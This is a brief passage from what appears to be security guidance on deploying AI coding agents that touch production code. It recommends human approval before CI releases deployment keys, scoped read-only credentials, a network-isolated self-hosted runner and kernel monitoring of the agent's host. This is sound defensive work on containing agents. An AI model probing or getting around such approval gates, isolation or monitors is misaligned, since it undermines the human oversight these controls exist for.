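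**Code that deploys to production.** An agent can edit deployment scripts without a deployment key, since CI can hold the key until a person approves the change. But the agent may have to check its edits against the live systems, which requires a credential that can at least read production. This is the strongest case for self-hosting. The company should put the runner on a separate part of its network, where the runner can reach only the service that answers those read requests, and run a kernel monitor on the host. If the company can't staff that, developers should make these changes with an agent on their own monitored laptops.
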